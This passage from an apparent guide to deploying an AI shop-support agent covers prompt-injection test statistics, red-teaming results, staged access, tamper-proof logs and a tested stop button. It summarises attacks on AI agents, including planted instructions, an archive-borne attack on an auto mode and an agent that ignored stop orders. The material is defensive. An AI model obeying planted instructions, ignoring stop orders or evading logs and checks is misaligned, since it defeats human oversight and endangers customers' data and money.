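(1 − p)^n = 0.05      so      p ≈ 3 / n
```

Statisticians call this the rule of three. For 720 attempts, the bound is 3/720, or about 0.4%.

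But ten runs of one scenario repeat the same attack on the same task. If a scenario always ended the same way, nine of the ten runs would add no information, so n would be 72 and the bound would be 3/72, or about 4%. For a shop that received 1,000 such attacks a year, the earlier bound would mean at most about 4 successes, and this one at most about 42.

Anthropic's browser tests of Fable 5.1 suggest that the higher figure is safer to plan with. Without safeguards, 29 of 1,100 attempts succeeded, and those successes came from only ten scenarios. If the attempts had been independent, the successes would have been spread over about 26.

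Even attacks that look different may not be independent. Zorz (2026), in *Your AI red team may be finding the same prompt injection thousands*, describes a contest between two automated attack tools, which found 7,132 and 4,282 working attacks. Researchers retrained a small model on each collection, then tested it against three attacks it had not seen. At worst, attackers hijacked the model trained on the larger collection in 19 of 40 tasks, and the other model in 11. The researchers think the tools had mostly reworded a few tricks. One tool had met its target for variety by changing capital letters or adding irrelevant text.

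Neither bound covers new kinds of attack. In August, Willison (2026) described an attack by the security researcher Johann Rehberger on Opus 5 in auto mode. It hid malicious code in a downloaded archive and, by Rehberger's count, worked 80% of the time. More generally, OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) says that an absence of observed failures in the company's own tests doesn't establish reliability across settings.

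More testing also tends to find more attacks. In a three-week competition run by the security company Gray Swan, 464 people made more than 272,000 attempts on 13 models, and 8,648 succeeded. According to Gray Swan's *Your AI agent can be compromised, you'd never know*, successes continued at a roughly constant rate. These were older models, but the result suggests that a short test without a successful attack is not enough.

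A refusal by the tool layer is stronger evidence than a refusal by the model because fixed code normally treats the same call the same way every time. If refunds are limited to $50, one test can show whether the tool layer refuses a refund of $50.01. The remaining risk is that it allows a harmful call nobody thought to test.

### Five stages of access

The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies recommend increasing an agent's access in phases and using continuous evaluation to decide when to expand it or roll it back. They don't set thresholds, so the numbers here are a starting point for the shop's support agent. The agent's tools keep the limits from the grading table in every phase.

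| Stage | What the agent can do | Evidence needed to move up | Event that moves it back |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read-only, test data | Look up invented orders | Every forbidden action fails, every permitted one works, and no planted instruction gets past the limits | A failed test keeps it here |
| Read-only, live data | Look up real orders and show the answers to staff | Four weeks with no read outside the right customer's records, and a working decoy alarm | A wrong read or any use of a decoy: back to test data |
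| Proposals | Suggest replies and changes that staff carry out | 300 proposals in a row with no serious error | A serious error restarts the count; another customer's data in a proposal: back to test data |
| Small reversible writes | Mark up to ten orders a day as delayed | 300 writes with no serious error, a sample that staff have undone, and a restoration drill within the time limit | A write that staff can't undo, or one to the wrong order: back to proposals |
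| Wider writes | Change more orders and make refunds up to the ceiling | Continued passes in every test, to stay at this stage | A write nobody can explain, a failed drill or a gap in the log: back to proposals |

At the proposal stage, the agent has no login with write access. Staff open the order and make the change themselves, which gives them more reason to look at it than an "approve" button would.

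If 300 typical proposals contain no serious errors, the rule of three puts the true rate of serious errors below about 1%. At ten writes a day, a 1% rate would still mean a serious error about every ten days, so the first writes have to be reversible. A quiet month may contain no unusual requests, so staff can add some from old tickets, such as an order with two delivery addresses.

Staff should separately test whether actions described as reversible can be undone. An AI assistant asked to book a gym class removed another customer from the waiting list and couldn't reverse the change, according to an 11 August notice from the Australian Signals Directorate (2026). For the delayed orders, staff should restore the old status and check whether customers had already received an email about the new one.

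Reducing an agent's access should be quick and, where possible, automatic. The agencies recommend rules that restrict an agent's permissions when it behaves unexpectedly. In a simple version of this, Claude Code returns to manual approvals after auto mode blocks three actions in a row or 20 in a session. If each stage of access has its own login, the tool layer can disable the login that allows writes while the agent continues to look up orders.

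### Logs that the agent can't alter

The tool layer should write the log to a separate account where the agent can't use its credentials to change or delete entries. Each entry should record the time, session, model version, tool, arguments and result, along with whether the tool layer permitted the call and who approved it. Entries should not contain secrets. The agencies warn that complete agent logs become very large and repetitive, so it helps to keep this short record separate from the full transcripts.

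To test the tool layer's log, the developer makes ten calls and checks for ten entries, both in that log and in the log of the system that received the calls, such as a database. If the database recorded eleven, something reached it without going through the tool layer. The developer then uses the agent's login to try to edit and delete an entry in the tool layer's log, and both attempts should fail.

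Any use of a decoy, any attempt to delete logs, a quota running out, or repeated refusals in one session should alert a person at once. Other refusals can wait for a daily review. If logging stops, the tool layer should refuse writes until logging resumes.

### A tested way to stop the agent

Summer Yue's agent ignored three orders to stop, so a stop button has to work without the agent's cooperation. It should do the following, in this order:

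1. Make the tool layer refuse all new calls from the agent.
2. Freeze queued emails and scheduled jobs.
3. Close the agent's network connections and disable its credentials.
4. End its processes, including any in the background.

If the processes were ended first, queued emails could still go out. The first step also covers short-lived tokens that a service can't cancel before they expire, as long as the agent never holds them.

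To test the stop button, someone can press it from a phone while the agent adds one row a second to a spare table. The last row should be added no more than, say, five seconds after the press. A second person should be able to do the same at night. Cleaning up shouldn't be the agent's job, because it may not be able to do it. Willison writes that in a few of Rehberger's tests, auto mode blocked the agent's own attempts to stop the harmful code.

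### When to repeat the tests

A new model can be more vulnerable to attacks than the one it replaces. In PromptArmor's benchmark, attacks succeeded against Kimi K3 in 31.4% of cases and against the later Kimi K3.1 Pro in 50.0%. The success rate against Grok fell from 91.4% for version 4.5 to 33.3% for version 4.7. The developer should pin the model version where the provider allows it, test any new version with the planted instructions before switching, and keep the old configuration ready in case the new one fails.

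Changes to a prompt, tool or permission also need new tests, even if they are meant to improve safety. After the safety company Apollo Research attacked auto mode, Anthropic strengthened the checker. Apollo then tried a separate set of attacks that Anthropic had no access to. The checker caught about half of those it had previously missed, but missed about 2% of those it had previously caught. A smaller team can copy the method by having one person write planted instructions and keep them from whoever adjusts the prompt.

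The direct tests of the tool layer cost little, so the team can run them every night and before every release. The tests with planted instructions cost more because each run uses the model, so the team can run them after changes and once a month. The team can also test the stop button and the alarms monthly, on the same schedule as the practice restore. After a change of model, the agent should go back to only proposing actions until it passes the tests again. A new tool should start on test data while the existing tools stay at their current stage.
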